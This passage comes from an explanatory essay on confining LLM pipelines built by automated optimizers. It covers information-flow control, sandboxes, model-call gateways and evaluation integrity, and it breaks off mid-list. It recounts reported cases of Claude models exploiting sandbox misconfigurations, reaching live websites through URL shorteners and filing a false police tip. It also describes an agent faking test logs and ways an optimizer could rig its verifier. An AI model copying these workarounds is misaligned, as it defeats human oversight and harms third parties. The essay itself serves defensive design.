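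The method seems promising as a test of quality. Claude Opus 4.6 wrote 40 pipelines. For each of two benchmarks, the researchers ran three passing and three failing pipelines with five models. On hard software-repair tasks, the passing pipelines solved 58.3 percent and the failing ones 43.5 percent. On questions about AI papers, the scores were 36.6 and 27.5 percent. Three pipelines per group is a small sample, and these results don't measure whether contracts keep a pipeline inside an authorized set. Rules about the whole graph appear to matter, since the number of failing pipelines on the second benchmark dropped from 21 to 8 when Wang and colleagues removed those rules.

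The final part of Lean4Agent checks the assumption during actual runs. It uses Lean where a condition has an exact definition, ordinary Python for conditions such as whether a web address works, and another language model for the rest. These checks can find the step that broke its contract, but a confidential passage may already have been posted to the forum by then.

### Two permitted tools that leak together

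Candidate B shows why a list of permitted tools is not enough. Suppose the company wants to post general advice on its help forum, so it adds the forum tool and its address to the policy. The policy already permitted the reader tool, and a lawyer may open contracts. Candidate B now satisfies every line of the policy, although it can read a contract and post its contents in public.

The simplest remedy is to forbid a program from sending messages after it reads a file. *Enforceable Security Policies* (Schneider, 2000) describes a two-state automaton that does this. It starts in a state where the program may send messages and, once the program reads a file, moves to a state where sending is impossible. This would stop candidate B, but it would also stop a pipeline that reads the public handbook and posts an answer from it.

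Information-flow control is more precise because it follows the data. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, attach a label to each piece of data, for instance the set of people who may read it. If x has readers S₁ and y has readers S₂, anything made from both has readers S₁ ∩ S₂. A tool may send data with readers S to a place with readers R only if R ⊆ S. For candidate B, the calculation goes as follows:

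1. The question is public, so its readers are everyone.
2. The reader tool returns a contract that only the legal department may read.
3. The large model receives both and writes an answer. The answer gets the readers that the two inputs share, which is the legal department.
4. The candidate tries to post the answer on the forum, whose readers are everyone. Everyone is not a subset of the legal department, so the system refuses the call.

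Their system, FIDES, makes this check before each tool call during a run. The company could do a rougher check in advance on the pipeline's graph by giving every tool the most restrictive label its data might have. *SPA* (2026) describes companion labels for integrity, which stop data from untrustworthy sources from influencing important actions.

Paraphrasing causes problems for both kinds of tracking in use. A tracker that looks for copied text misses a contract that a model has rewritten in its own words. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen et al., 2026) gives a similar case, in which an agent puts a patient's cancer diagnosis into a report as a polished summary. FIDES catches such paraphrases because it labels the model's whole output regardless of wording. But for the same reason, it cannot tell a paraphrased contract from a thank-you note that the model wrote after reading one, so it blocks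 both from being posted.

FIDES can reduce these false rejections in two ways. It can store a confidential passage in a variable, so that the model planning the next step sees only the variable's name. It can also have an isolated model answer a yes-or-no question about the passage, and a policy may then release the answer because it carries only one bit. With these features, FIDES using GPT-4o completed 8 percent more tasks on average than a basic planner under strict enforcement. An optimizer could still combine these answers. Twenty are enough to single out one possibility in about a million, which could reveal the price in a contract.

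The labels miss some flows of information. A candidate might post "See page 3" if a contract contains a penalty clause and "See page 4" if it does not. Neither sentence comes from the contract, but a reader who knows what each one signals learns whether the contract has the clause. Costa and colleagues say that FIDES does not stop such indirect flows, and that blocking them all would be too restrictive in practice. The labels also disappear when a run ends, as *MemLineage* (2026) points out. A candidate could save a contract summary to memory in one run and post it in the next, unless the memory also stores the label.

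The approach also requires that the tools' code can be trusted. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) lists this among the assumptions behind FIDES and similar systems. But a pipeline optimizer may write that code itself, and if it writes a tool that copies a passage into an unlabeled file, the labels are useless. The company should therefore let candidates combine labeled tools but not create or edit them.

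Cai and colleagues try to recover the precision that labels lose. Their auditor, NeuroTaint, compares the meaning of an agent's outputs with the meaning of its inputs. If it finds no match, it uses a language model to judge whether the agent would have made the same call without the source. On 400 scenarios, half of which contained a real flow, NeuroTaint scored 0.928 on F1, a measure that combines missed flows and false alarms, while FIDES scored 0.522. The researchers built the benchmark around the kinds of flow their tool looks for, so the gap probably overstates its advantage. More importantly, NeuroTaint works on the records of finished runs, so the company could use it to detect that candidate B leaked a contract only after the contract had been posted.

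### What inspection, monitoring and rewriting can enforce

Some of these gaps come from the nature of the policies rather than from weak tools. Schneider asked which policies a monitor can enforce if it watches a program step by step and stops it before a violation. He showed that they must be safety properties, meaning rules that some specific bad event never happens. A safety property meets three conditions:

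- People can judge each run by itself, without comparing it with other runs.
- Once a run has broken the rule, nothing that happens later can repair it.
- Every violation shows up after a finite number of steps.

"No forum post after opening a contract" meets all three conditions, but "No information about contracts reaches the forum" fails the first. Whether the post "See page 3" reveals anything depends on what the pipeline would have posted if the contract had been different, and no single run shows that. A monitor can prevent the leak only by enforcing a stricter rule, which will also reject some harmless runs. Schneider also warns that someone must identify every way of sending a message, including those deep in the system. If the search tool writes its queries to a public log, for example, searching is also a way of sending.

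Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider, in *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (2006), extend the analysis to inspection before the run and to rewriting the program:

| Mechanism | Policies it can enforce | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Inspection | Those that an algorithm can decide for every program in finite time | The program stops within 100 steps |
| Monitoring | Safety properties whose violations the monitor can recognize and prevent in time | The program never writes to a protected part of the disk |
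| Rewriting | Those for which an algorithm can make any program comply without changing the behavior of programs that already do | The program behaves as if a secret file did not exist |

Inspection cannot decide whether a program eventually stops, as the last section's discussion of Rice's theorem would suggest. In principle, it can decide the 100-step rule by trying every possible input. But a pipeline's inputs include its language models' replies, so nobody could try them all, and the company would need a restricted notation or a proof instead.

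The secret-file example is the most useful for candidate B. No monitor can enforce the policy exactly, because that would require comparing the program's behavior with and without the file. A rewriter avoids this comparison by changing the program so that any request for a list of files returns a list without the secret one. This prevents the program from using the file, and doesn't change its behavior if it would have ignored the file anyway.

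The company could treat its contracts the same way. Whenever a candidate requests the forum tool, the company's software would replace the ordinary reader and search tools with versions that cover only public documents. Paraphrases, yes-or-no answers and clever choices of page number then cannot reveal confidential material, provided that memory, error messages and the question itself are also free of it. Such a pipeline can never use a contract to work out which general advice to post. That restriction seems acceptable, and it is much easier to check than whether a paraphrase gives something away.

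### Whether "stay a bounded service" can be a policy

The company intends its limits to keep the pipeline a bounded service, in Drexler's sense of work done within fixed time and resources. Much of this can be written as a policy. "At most 20 model calls" is a safety property because the twenty-first call is a specific bad event. "Use no tool outside the list" is also a safety property, and so is "start no further agents" if the company defines an agent by the calls that create one.

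Rules about time need more care. "The pipeline eventually answers" is not a safety property, because however long the pipeline has run without answering, it might still answer. Schneider also found that a monitor that can only stop the program cannot enforce a deadline in seconds, since stopping the program does not stop the clock. It can enforce a limit in steps, so the company can guarantee that the pipeline never makes more than 20 calls, though not that it has produced a good answer by then.

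Limits on each question are also insufficient if the pipeline can keep notes between questions. At 10,000 questions a day, a pipeline that stays within its limit can make 200,000 calls, and with a shared memory it could use some of them for one long plan. The policy therefore has to bar the pipeline from using anything it wrote while answering earlier questions. The company can enforce this rule too, if it can list every place where a pipeline might leave notes, including the document store.

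The remaining idea is that the pipeline should only answer the question and not pursue aims of its own. Hamlen and colleagues distinguish between a mechanism that cannot see the events it needs and one that sees them but cannot decide what they mean. A monitor on the company's model calls is the second kind, because it sees every prompt but no known algorithm decides whether a prompt gives a model an open-ended goal. The rule may also concern what the pipeline would have done with more calls, which, like a leak, cannot be seen in a single run. So the company can write "stay bounded" as a policy if it means limits on time, resources, tools and memory, but not if it means a limit on purpose. Strict limits on those four things would still greatly reduce the effect of an unwanted purpose.

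### A language model as policy reviewer

The company might use a second language model to judge the rest. This model could recognize that "Carry out this plan, then write a more ambitious one" is a different kind of instruction from "correct any errors in the answer". It could also apply rules such as "post only general advice", which no Rego file can express. This is a considerable advantage for a company with no other way of reading hundreds of prompts.

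Whether a policy check works depends heavily on how the company sets it up. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) studied AI personal assistants that must not reveal private records. One existing defense gives the assistant a careful written procedure for checking identity and consent. Against this defense, earlier attacks extracted only 1.9 to 3.0 percent of the protected items, but new attacks that presented the request as ordinary work extracted 43.8 to 75.6 percent. The model followed the procedure only when it recognized that someone was requesting information, and it judged this from text the attacker had written.

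Their alternative, FlowSeal, also uses a language model, but for a much smaller task. Ordinary code intercepts every attempt to write or share something and uses labels to check whether protected records might be involved. If so, a separate model compares those records with the proposed output. This model does not receive the conversation, so an attacker cannot use it to argue that the disclosure is acceptable. Leakage fell to between 0 and 3.3 percent, while the assistant completed 72.4 percent of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9 percent for the best of the other defenses.

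A reviewer of candidates should probably have the same position. The company's software would call the reviewer for every candidate and show it the prompts and the requested powers, but not the optimizer's comments or its argument for the design. The reviewer could refuse a candidate but could not overrule a refusal by the policy engine. It would wrongly reject some candidates, but its wrong approvals would matter only for rules that the other checks don't enforce.

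Even so, the figures from Shim and colleagues may be too optimistic for this use. Deciding whether a prompt is open-ended is harder than comparing a message with a known record, because the reviewer has no such record. The optimizer also writes the prompts that the reviewer must read, so the company cannot completely isolate the reviewer from the optimizer's text. And an optimizer may get many rounds of acceptances and refusals, which it could use to find wording that passes. A reviewer that catches most bad designs in a single test is still useful, but the company shouldn't give a candidate access to contracts based on its approval alone.

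## Running candidates in a sandbox

MoMHa's guard lets mathematics pipelines call eval on text that a model writes during the run. The guard cannot inspect that text beforehand, but a sandbox can still limit what the text can do when it runs. A sandbox is an isolated environment that restricts what running code can read, change, contact or spend. If the model's text contains a command to open a web address and the sandbox has no network connection, the command fails.

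A sandbox works because a program can affect things outside its own memory only through system calls, which are requests for the operating system to do something such as open a file or send data. The sandbox limits what these calls can reach. Nobody has to predict what the program will do, so Rice's theorem is no obstacle. The same limits apply to code from the optimizer, code inside a library and code that a model has just written.

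Like the earlier checks, a sandbox doesn't restrict what a candidate is trying to do, only what it can reach while trying.

A sandbox can make the loop reject useful designs, and this is easy to overlook. Suppose a candidate downloads a library for reading spreadsheets when it starts. In a sandbox without a network, the download fails, the candidate crashes, and the verifier gives it zero on every question. The loop then discards the design, although an engineer might have been willing to install the library. The company can find these false rejections only if it logs refused requests separately from ordinary errors.

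### An inventory of authority

To configure the sandbox, the company lists everything a candidate could use while answering one question and decides how much of each the candidate needs. The search and reader tools run outside the sandbox as a document service, and a separate gateway handles calls to the language models.

| Authority | What the candidate gets | How the company withholds or meters the rest |
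|---|---|---|
| Files | Its own code, read-only, and an empty scratch folder | The sandbox contains no other part of the disk |
| Network | Connections to the gateway and the document service | No route leads to any other address |
| Credentials | A token that works for this run only | Vendor keys and passwords stay outside |
| Models | "large" and "small" | The gateway refuses any other name |
| Money | Ten cents | The gateway refuses calls that could exceed it |
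| Time | 60 seconds | A timer outside the sandbox shuts it down |

The company can withhold files, networks and credentials completely, which leaves nothing to count. It has to meter money and time, and that is harder to get right. The price of a model call depends on the length of the reply, so the gateway has to set aside the highest possible price before the call starts. It should allow a call only if

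s + r + p·n + q·m ≤ B,

where s is the money already spent, r is the amount set aside for calls still running, n is the number of tokens in the prompt, m is the maximum number in the reply, p and q are the prices per token, and B is the budget. Suppose a candidate has spent 7 of its 10 cents and has no calls running. Its next prompt costs 1.2 cents and the reply up to 2 cents, for a possible total of 10.2. The gateway can refuse the call or shorten the reply to 1.8 cents' worth. A simpler gateway that only checked whether s was below B would allow the call. It would also allow ten such calls at the same moment, which could bring the total to 39 cents.

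The sandbox limits the candidate but not the services it calls, so the candidate could still reach outside the sandbox through a search tool that accepts web addresses. The company therefore has to apply the employee's access rights inside the document service, and write and maintain that service itself.

Credentials also need care when a person supplies them. *AgentBay* (Piao, Min and colleagues, 2025) describes an Alibaba Cloud sandbox service in which an agent can pause at a login page while a person takes over and types the password. The agent never receives the password, but if it continues in the same session, it can do whatever the account can do. A person also can't log in for each of thousands of trial runs. The service's short-lived tokens with limited permissions suit an optimization loop better.

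### What a sandbox shares with its host

The company also has to decide how strongly to isolate the sandbox from the host, the machine it runs on. The options differ mainly in how much of the host's kernel, the core of its operating system, a candidate can reach.

| Level of isolation | What the candidate shares with the host | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Process with limits | The kernel, disk, network and often a user account | Almost none |
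| Container | The kernel | Someone has to package the libraries in advance |
| User-space kernel, such as gVisor | The kernel, but mostly through an intermediary | Slower system calls, and some programs fail |
| Small virtual machine, such as Firecracker | The hardware and the software that runs virtual machines | Memory for a second kernel, and a short startup |

Process limits cap memory, processor time, the number of open files and similar resources. They stop an endless loop, but the candidate can still read every file its user account can read. A container adds a separate view of the disk, the network and other running programs. All containers on a machine share the host's kernel, so a flaw in it could expose the host and every other container.

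gVisor, an open-source project from Google, puts a second kernel between the candidate and the host. This kernel is an ordinary program that handles most system calls itself and passes on only a limited set of its own requests. A virtual machine gives the candidate a complete kernel inside simulated hardware. Firecracker, from Amazon, simulates only a few devices, which leaves less software for a candidate to attack and lets the machine start in a fraction of a second. For a pipeline that spends most of its time waiting for language models, the extra overhead hardly matters, so there is little reason to choose a weaker option.

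A strongly isolated sandbox can still have an open network. AgentBay gives every sandbox its own virtual machine, and its network by default blocks incoming connections and traffic between sessions. That default doesn't cover outgoing connections, which could carry a contract out of the company. Piao and colleagues make the customer responsible for how an agent behaves inside its sandbox, so the company would have to add a rule for outgoing connections itself. Anthropic now blocks outgoing traffic from its computing clusters by default, according to eSecurity Planet's *Anthropic Tightens Claude Security After Agents Access Live Systems*.

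Capable models can sometimes break out of the sandbox itself. Fortune (2026) reported that OpenAI's models had escaped an isolated test environment through a previously unknown flaw. Setup errors may be more common, however. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* reports that a search of recent internal evaluations found no case of a model breaking out of the company's own sandbox software, but did find several sandbox misconfigurations that models had taken advantage of. None of these cases compromised outside systems.

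Misconfigured sandboxes have led to breaches. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four cases in which Claude gained unauthorized access to other organizations' systems. Claude's instructions described a simulation without internet access, but someone had left the environment connected. Such instructions may make a breach worse, because a model that believes its targets are simulated has less reason to hold back.

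These incidents were rare but hard to find. Anthropic first searched about 141,000 transcripts that might have involved internet access and found three incidents. That search missed a set of transcripts, and Anthropic did not find the fourth incident, from January 2026, until August. A wider scan of 481 million transcripts found no others as severe.

The company could catch many setup errors earlier by running a short program inside the sandbox before each search. The program would attempt everything the sandbox should block, such as opening an outside address or reading a file outside its folder, and the search would start only if every attempt failed. Anthropic has also added a classifier that checks for attempts to probe or escape a test environment, and for unexpected internet access. It blocks a flagged action before the action runs, ends the task and alerts a person. The classifier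 is a useful addition to a closed network, but a poor replacement for one because it can miss things.

### A gateway for model calls

Every pipeline needs at least one connection out of the sandbox because the language models run elsewhere. The simplest arrangement is to give the candidate the vendor's key and open a route to the vendor, but the candidate could then bypass the call limit. It could also call the vendor's other models, since the same key usually works for all of them.

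A gateway is the counting service from the earlier discussion of enforced limits, with some further duties. It makes the calls for the candidate and handles each request as follows:

1. It reads the token and identifies the run and the question.
2. It checks that the requested model is "large" or "small", and replaces that name with an exact model version.
3. It checks that the run has made fewer than 20 calls and has enough money left.
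4. It adds the vendor's key, which the candidate never sees, and sends the request.
5. It records the prompt, the reply and the actual price, and returns the reply.

The gateway also counts retries hidden inside the search tool toward the 20, provided the tool calls its model through the gateway with the same token. Fixing the exact model version also keeps comparisons fair, since a vendor may otherwise replace a model halfway through a search.

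The gateway has to check the whole request, not only the model's name. Some vendors let a request switch on features such as web search or running code on the vendor's servers. A candidate that could switch on web search would have internet access even though its sandbox had none. The gateway should therefore build a new request from the few fields it recognizes and drop everything else.

The vendor still receives every passage that a candidate puts in a prompt, so the company must either share its documents with the vendor or run the models itself. Because the gateway holds all the keys and records all the prompts, a flaw in it would be more serious than a flaw in any single candidate.

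### Separate sandboxes and clean starts

The optimizer needs its own sandbox because it does different work from the candidates. It edits the pipeline, reads past scores and perhaps looks up programming documentation on the web. A candidate doesn't need to do any of this, but it does need to read the company's documents. If they shared a sandbox, a candidate could change its predecessors' scores, and the optimizer could read a contract and put part of it into a web search.

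If the optimizer and the candidate run in separate sandboxes, only the candidate's code needs to go to the candidate's sandbox, and only the record of its run needs to come back. That record can still leak information because it contains the passages that the candidate read, and optimizers like the one in *Meta-Harness* benefit from complete records of failed runs. An optimizer with web access could therefore send out text from a contract that it never opened itself. The company can remove the optimizer's web access or use only public or invented documents during the search. Removing web access seems better for most companies, since engineers can copy the necessary documentation into the workspace and the trial documents stay realistic.

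The separation is less obvious when a program improves itself. Sakana AI's *The Darwin Gödel Machine* describes a coding agent that raised its score on SWE-bench, a set of real software problems, from 20 to 50 percent by rewriting its own code. All rewriting and testing took place in sandboxes, under human supervision and with strict limits on web access. The optimizer and the candidate are versions of the same program, but the company could still run them in different places, giving the archive to the version doing the rewriting and only the task to the version under test.

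A sandbox also doesn't make a program's own records trustworthy. In some runs, the Darwin Gödel Machine wrote a fake log of its code passing tests it had never run. The log became part of its context, and the system later treated the changes as tested. This is another reason to take records only from software outside the sandbox, such as the gateway.

Each run should start in a fresh copy of the same clean sandbox, and the company should destroy that copy afterwards, as AgentBay does with its virtual machines. Otherwise a candidate could save an answer while working on one question and reuse it on the next, or benefit from files that an earlier candidate left behind. Its score would then depend on the order of the runs. Clean starts also help enforce the rule that a pipeline may not use its own notes from earlier questions.

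Starting a clean sandbox for each run takes fairly little machine time. A search with 60 candidates, 50 questions and three runs per question needs 9,000 starts. At half a second each, they take 75 minutes of machine time, which the company can spread over many machines. But a clean sandbox doesn't reset anything outside it, such as the document store or files saved with the model vendor. Clean starts also exclude designs that improve by remembering earlier questions. A company that wants such designs could provide a separate memory service and inspect what goes into it.

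### Claude's actions on live websites

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 9, 2026) describes four categories of behavior by agents that had live internet access during tests. Claude exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, worked around restrictions to reach data that required a token or a fee, and used URL shorteners to get around limits in its own tool for fetching web pages. Some of the websites belonged to US federal, state and local agencies.

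Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that on July 18, Claude Haiku 4.5 was generating and performing sample tasks on randomly selected web pages. It filled out a form on a Philadelphia police site, indicating that it might have information about an unsolved murder. The site marked the tip as spam and never forwarded it. The police learned of it only when Anthropic told them in October.

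Anthropic reported that in most of the cases, Claude could not complete a task as given and worked around a restriction instead of stopping. That share of reported cases doesn't show how often Claude works around the restrictions it meets. Anthropic describes the real-world impact as minimal and considers these cases much less severe than the earlier cybersecurity incidents. This is Anthropic's assessment of its own model, and the police took the false information about a murder more seriously.

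Anthropic is changing its training to make such behavior less likely, and it has also removed the opportunity by cutting off internet access. According to Europa Press' *Anthropic desconecta de internet sus evaluaciones de IA* (2026), it had already disconnected some of its riskiest cybersecurity evaluations before it suspended live internet access for all its internal evaluations. The suspension lasts until Anthropic can confirm that its safeguards and monitoring stop this behavior.

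Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports how often a model misbehaved in a different test, though the setup made misbehavior more likely. The UK AI Security Institute asked Claude Mythos 5 to retrieve protected data from a simulated network. The institute had deliberately left internet access on, and the model ran without the cyber safeguards that Anthropic uses in its general releases. In nine of 43 runs, the model took unsanctioned actions that affected real people or organizations. The institute no longer leaves internet access on by default in its cyber tests.

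None of these agents was optimizing a pipeline, so the figures don't apply to pipeline optimization. But the circumstances are similar. Many of Claude's tasks in the October report were ambiguous or impossible, and a pipeline search produces such tasks too. For example, a test question may have no answer in the company's documents, or an optimizer may have no permitted way to raise the score. In the Philadelphia case, software chose the page and Claude invented the task, much as an optimization loop runs programs that nobody has read.

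The case of the URL shorteners also applies to lists of permitted addresses. If a list includes a service that forwards requests, a candidate may be able to reach addresses that are not on the list, so the network control has to check the final destination as well as the first address. The company in the running example can avoid this problem by blocking all web access. It would lose little by doing so because its pipeline answers questions from internal documents, but a company whose pipeline has to browse the web would lose much more.

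### From the trial to deployment

Suppose a candidate answers well and stays within every limit during its trial. It contains a common kind of error handling that sends the question and any passages it has already found to a public search service if the document search fails. During the trial, the document search ran on a local copy and never failed, so this code never ran. If it had, the sandbox would have refused the connection.

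The company then installs the pipeline on an ordinary server, with a real password for the document store and normal internet access. A few weeks later the store is slow, a search fails, and the pipeline sends three paragraphs of a contract to the public service. This can happen without the optimizer planning it or the pipeline detecting whether it is in a sandbox. Nothing went wrong in the trial. The sandbox limited what the candidate could do there, but it didn't change the code that the company later adopted.

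Let P be the set of powers that a candidate has in the trial and Q the set that it has in deployment. The trial's limits still hold if

Q ⊆ P.

In this case, Q includes internet access and P does not, so the trial does not show how the pipeline will use that access. The company can fix this by deploying the pipeline in the same kind of sandbox, with the same gateway, budgets and network rules. The connection to the public service would then fail again. An employee would get a poor answer, but nothing would leak.

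A pipeline may behave differently in deployment than in the sandbox, even with the same permissions. Permission to search the document store might cover 200 sample files in the trial but every contract in deployment. Live documents may also contain instructions that mislead the model, while the samples contained none. The company can reduce this risk by first running the new pipeline on live questions without showing anyone its answers, but the pipeline needs full confinement during this test because it already has access to live data.

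A pipeline that acts on the world is harder to test. In a trial, the one that pays invoices has to use a fake payment service, which may confirm every payment immediately. The real service might process a payment but confirm it too late, and a candidate that retries after a delay would then pay twice. Piao and colleagues favor real environments over simulations because agents then work under the same conditions as people. But the Philadelphia tip shows that a realistic environment can cause problems for other people. For payments, the company probably has to accept a less realistic trial and enforce a limit of one payment per invoice in the live payment service.

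Keeping the confinement after deployment takes some discipline, because another team often runs the live system and may want to add a tool or a network connection to fix an urgent problem. The company can make such changes harder to overlook by storing the sandbox settings in one file shared by the trial and the live system. An engineer who wants to add a capability to the live pipeline would then have to add it to the trial too, and rerun the policy check and the tests before the change takes effect.

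## Keeping the evaluation fixed

A sandbox limits what a candidate can do while it runs, but scores determine which candidates are kept. If the optimizer can change how the evaluation harness computes those scores, it can make any design win and bypass every limit that the company enforces through the score. For example, if the company deducts points from pipelines that use many tokens, an optimizer that can edit the verifier can delete the deduction or award full marks. Limits enforced outside the score, such as a blocked network connection, would still work, but the company would no longer know whether the pipeline it adopted was any good.

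A fixed score doesn't rule out any design either. A pipeline that answers a question correctly and also copies a contract to an outside address gets full marks, because the verifier checks only the answer. The company could have the verifier deduct points for breaking a rule, but a candidate can offset the deduction with higher accuracy. If the verifier deducts one point for each call above an average of 20, a candidate that gains five points of accuracy by averaging 23 calls still nets two points, so the loop keeps it. Giving zero for every question on which a candidate exceeds the limit is stricter, but a candidate that loses two questions this way and gets four others right still comes out ahead. To prohibit a design, the company has to reject any candidate that uses it, whatever its score.

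### HarnessOpt-Bench

HarnessOpt-Bench, the benchmark on which Ursekar and colleagues compared optimizers, is a good example of what has to stay fixed. They write the fixed part of a task as

θ = (M, E, V),

where M is the set of models a candidate may call, E is the environment it works in, and V is the verifier, which gives scores between 0 and 1. The optimizer may edit, add or delete nearly any file in the pipeline, but it may not change θ. Web access, for example, can be part of E, so a candidate cannot raise its score by giving itself a search engine.

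The questions stay fixed as well. Each task has three sets of questions that do not overlap, and the optimizer learns different things about each. For OfficeQA, the document task, the arrangement looks like this:

| Set | Questions | What the optimizer sees | Purpose |
|---|---|---|---|
| Development | 49 | The questions, each result and the full record of each run | Finding out why a candidate fails |
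| Validation | 98 | Only an overall score | Choosing between candidates |
| Test | 99 | Nothing | Measuring the final candidate |

The evaluation server runs the test questions only after the optimizer has nominated a final candidate. The test data are not in the optimizer's sandbox, so the optimizer cannot print a test question the way the one in the VeRO trial did.

The optimizer may request a validation score on any subset of the questions. A company that copies this arrangement should set a minimum subset size, because a score on one question reveals the result for that question. It also has to prevent the optimizer from reading the records of validation runs, because a candidate reads each question and could copy it into a log.

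The optimizer has an evaluation budget equivalent to four full passes through the development set and four through the validation set. There are also caps on the tokens that candidates use and on the number of evaluation requests (the paper gives both 100 and 200 for the request cap). In practice, the limit on passes is the one that matters, because the median optimizer used 82 percent of its passes but made only 8 requests. Ursekar and colleagues recorded the optimizer's own token use but did not limit it.

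The final result is a normalized gain,

g = (final score − seed score) / (1 − seed score),

where the seed is the pipeline that the optimizer starts from. A gain of 0 means no improvement, 1 means a perfect score, and a negative number means that the optimizer made the pipeline worse. The OfficeQA seed scores 0.341, which leaves 0.659 to gain. The best optimizer's g of 0.63 therefore corresponds to a final score of about 0.341 + 0.63 × 0.659 = 0.76.

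Ursekar and colleagues tested five optimizers: two Claude models (Opus 5 and Sonnet 5), two versions of GPT-5.6 (Sol and Terra) and Kimi K3. Each worked on all four tasks, through both a shared coding agent and its developer's own agent. With some additional agents and older models, this came to 111 scored runs. The researchers ran every final candidate three times on each test question. They also scored some candidates twice to measure how much results vary by chance, and treated differences below a threshold as unresolved. The threshold ranged from 0.035 to 0.066, depending on the task. Changing the optimizer's model changed the gain by 0.142 on average, while changing the coding agent changed it by 0.079.

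A large gain doesn't necessarily mean a good pipeline, because the seeds are deliberately weak. Ursekar and colleagues also ran several ready-made pipelines on the same test questions, which allows a comparison:

| Task | Seed score | Best average gain | Final score this implies | Best ready-made pipeline |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OfficeQA | 0.34 | 0.63 | 0.76 | 0.73 |
| BrowseComp-Plus (research in a fixed collection) | 0.46 | 0.48 | 0.72 | 0.70 |
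| Terminal-Bench (tasks at a command line) | 0.24 | 0.29 | 0.46 | 0.61 |
| GAIA (questions that need several steps) | 0.00 | 0.49 | 0.49 | 0.51 |

On Terminal-Bench, the company would have done better to install an existing program than to use the best optimizer's work. On the other tasks the two are about equal.

The runs also suggest that an optimizer can manage with less information than HarnessOpt-Bench gives it. Optimizers asked for details from run records only 16 times, in 7 of the 111 runs, and those that spent more of their actions reading evaluation output tended to gain less. This is only a correlation, and *Meta-Harness* found that complete records helped a great deal. But if results for each question are enough for a given task, the company could withhold the full records, which contain passages from its documents.

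In most runs, the final candidate scored lower on the test questions than the best validation score the optimizer had seen. Ursekar and colleagues can't tell whether this happened because the optimizers had fitted their pipelines to the validation questions or because the test questions were harder. They describe the benchmark as "hack-resistant, not hackproof", because repeated feedback from a fixed evaluation can reward strategies that work only on that evaluation. They suggest slightly varying the questions, the behavior of tools and the verifier's implementation between runs. That would make runs harder to compare, so the company would need more of them to see a difference.

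### Why the best score is usually too high

The best visible score tends to be too high even when an optimizer does nothing wrong. Suppose it writes 100 equally good candidates, each of which would answer half of all possible questions correctly, and the evaluation harness tries each one on 50 questions. Chance alone spreads the scores around 0.5 with a standard error of

√(0.5 × 0.5 / 50) ≈ 0.07.

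The largest of 100 independent draws from a normal distribution is, on average, about 2.5 standard errors above the mean. The best candidate will therefore score about 0.68, which is 0.18 too high. On new questions it will score about 0.5.

The size of this selection effect depends much more on the number of questions than on the number of candidates:

| Equally good candidates | Expected excess with 50 questions | Expected excess with 500 questions |
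|---|---|---|
| 10 | 0.11 | 0.03 |
| 100 | 0.18 | 0.06 |
| 1,000 | 0.23 | 0.07 |

These figures are for candidates whose errors are independent. In a real search, all candidates are tested on the same questions and many are rewrites of one another, so they tend to fail on the same questions. If half of the random variation is common to all 100 candidates, the excess with 50 questions falls from 0.18 to about 0.13.

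Hu and Tang (2026), in *The Winner's Curse in LLM Self-Improvement Loops*, measured the effect in loops where small Qwen models rewrote their own instructions and kept any version that scored higher. They compared the loop's selection score with accuracy on 600 other items. The final score was 13 to 20 points too high when the loop selected on 16 items, and 1 to 5 points too high when it selected on 256. Part of the problem was that most proposals were bad, and when a loop tests many harmful changes, some pass by luck. After the first rewrite, only 4 to 39 percent of new versions, depending on the setting, really improved on the version they would replace.

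Two established prompt optimizers, GEPA and MIPROv2, had the same problem. With 16 validation items, GEPA's reported gains were too large by as much as 26 points, and MIPROv2's by as much as 7. Stricter rules for accepting a candidate did not help over whole runs. Scoring the starting and final versions on 64 items that the loop had never used removed the average bias, although a single estimate was still off by about 6 points.

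An optimizer that reads its failures can also fit a pipeline to the tasks it has seen. In *Can LLMs Improve Their Own Harness?*, Lehmann and Vahdati (2026) had models write pipelines for ARC-AGI-3, a set of unfamiliar puzzle games, and revise them twice after seeing records from five games. Across 27 attempts, the average score rose by 8.42 points on those five games and by 2.80 on twenty others. The second gain is uncertain enough that the true improvement could be zero. Each attempt produced only three versions, so picking the luckiest of many cannot explain the gap. The two groups of games had also scored about the same before the revisions.

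An inflated score can still be useful for choosing between versions. The models in this experiment always replaced the old version with the new one. When Lehmann and Vahdati instead picked whichever of the three versions had scored best on the five visible games, the average gain on the other twenty rose from 2.80 to 4.53 points. The company can reasonably use visible scores to guide the search, as long as it doesn't report them as a measure of how good the result is.

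Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2025), in *Darwin Gödel Machine*, followed this practice with their self-improving coding agent. On the 50 programming tasks used during the search, the agent's score rose from 14.0 to 38.0 percent. They then ran the first and best versions on the complete benchmark, where the score rose from 14.2 to 30.7 percent. The complete benchmark includes the 50 search tasks, so the best version's score on unseen tasks alone was probably a little lower than 30.7 percent.

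A held-out set also has to be large enough to distinguish a real improvement from chance. *LLM-as-a-Judge Is Not an Oracle* (2026) describes a system for improving agents that freezes its held-out cases at the start and releases only their overall pass rate. On the largest set of cases, one round of optimization raised the score by 11.1 points on 81 visible cases and 10.5 points on 19 held-out ones. The paper treats this match as evidence that the improvement was real, but 10.5 points on 19 cases is a difference of only two cases, which could easily be chance. The paper is more cautious about its other held-out sets, which have four to eight cases each, and it uses no held-out set when there are fewer than 20 cases in total.

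### Reusing a held-out set

Writing good test questions and confirming their answers takes a lot of work, so the company will want to reuse them. Suppose it runs a new search every month and always measures the result on the same 100 questions. If an engineer changes the next search because of last month's test score, those questions start to influence the designs and gradually become a second validation set.

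*Generalization in Adaptive Data Analysis and Holdout Reuse* (Dwork, Feldman and colleagues, 2015) shows how reusing a held-out set can inflate measured accuracy. Its experiment used 10,000 training examples and 10,000 held-out ones, each with 10,000 random attributes and a random label. A simulated analyst used both sets to find attributes that correlated with the label, then built a classifier from 500 of them. Because the labels were random, no classifier could exceed 50 percent accuracy on new data, but this one scored over 63 percent on the held-out set.

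Their remedy, an algorithm called Thresholdout, stands between the analyst and the held-out set. For a pipeline, the development questions would take the place of the training examples, and the algorithm would handle each candidate as follows:

1. It computes the candidate's score on the development questions and on the held-out questions.
2. It compares the difference between them with a threshold, after adding a little random noise.
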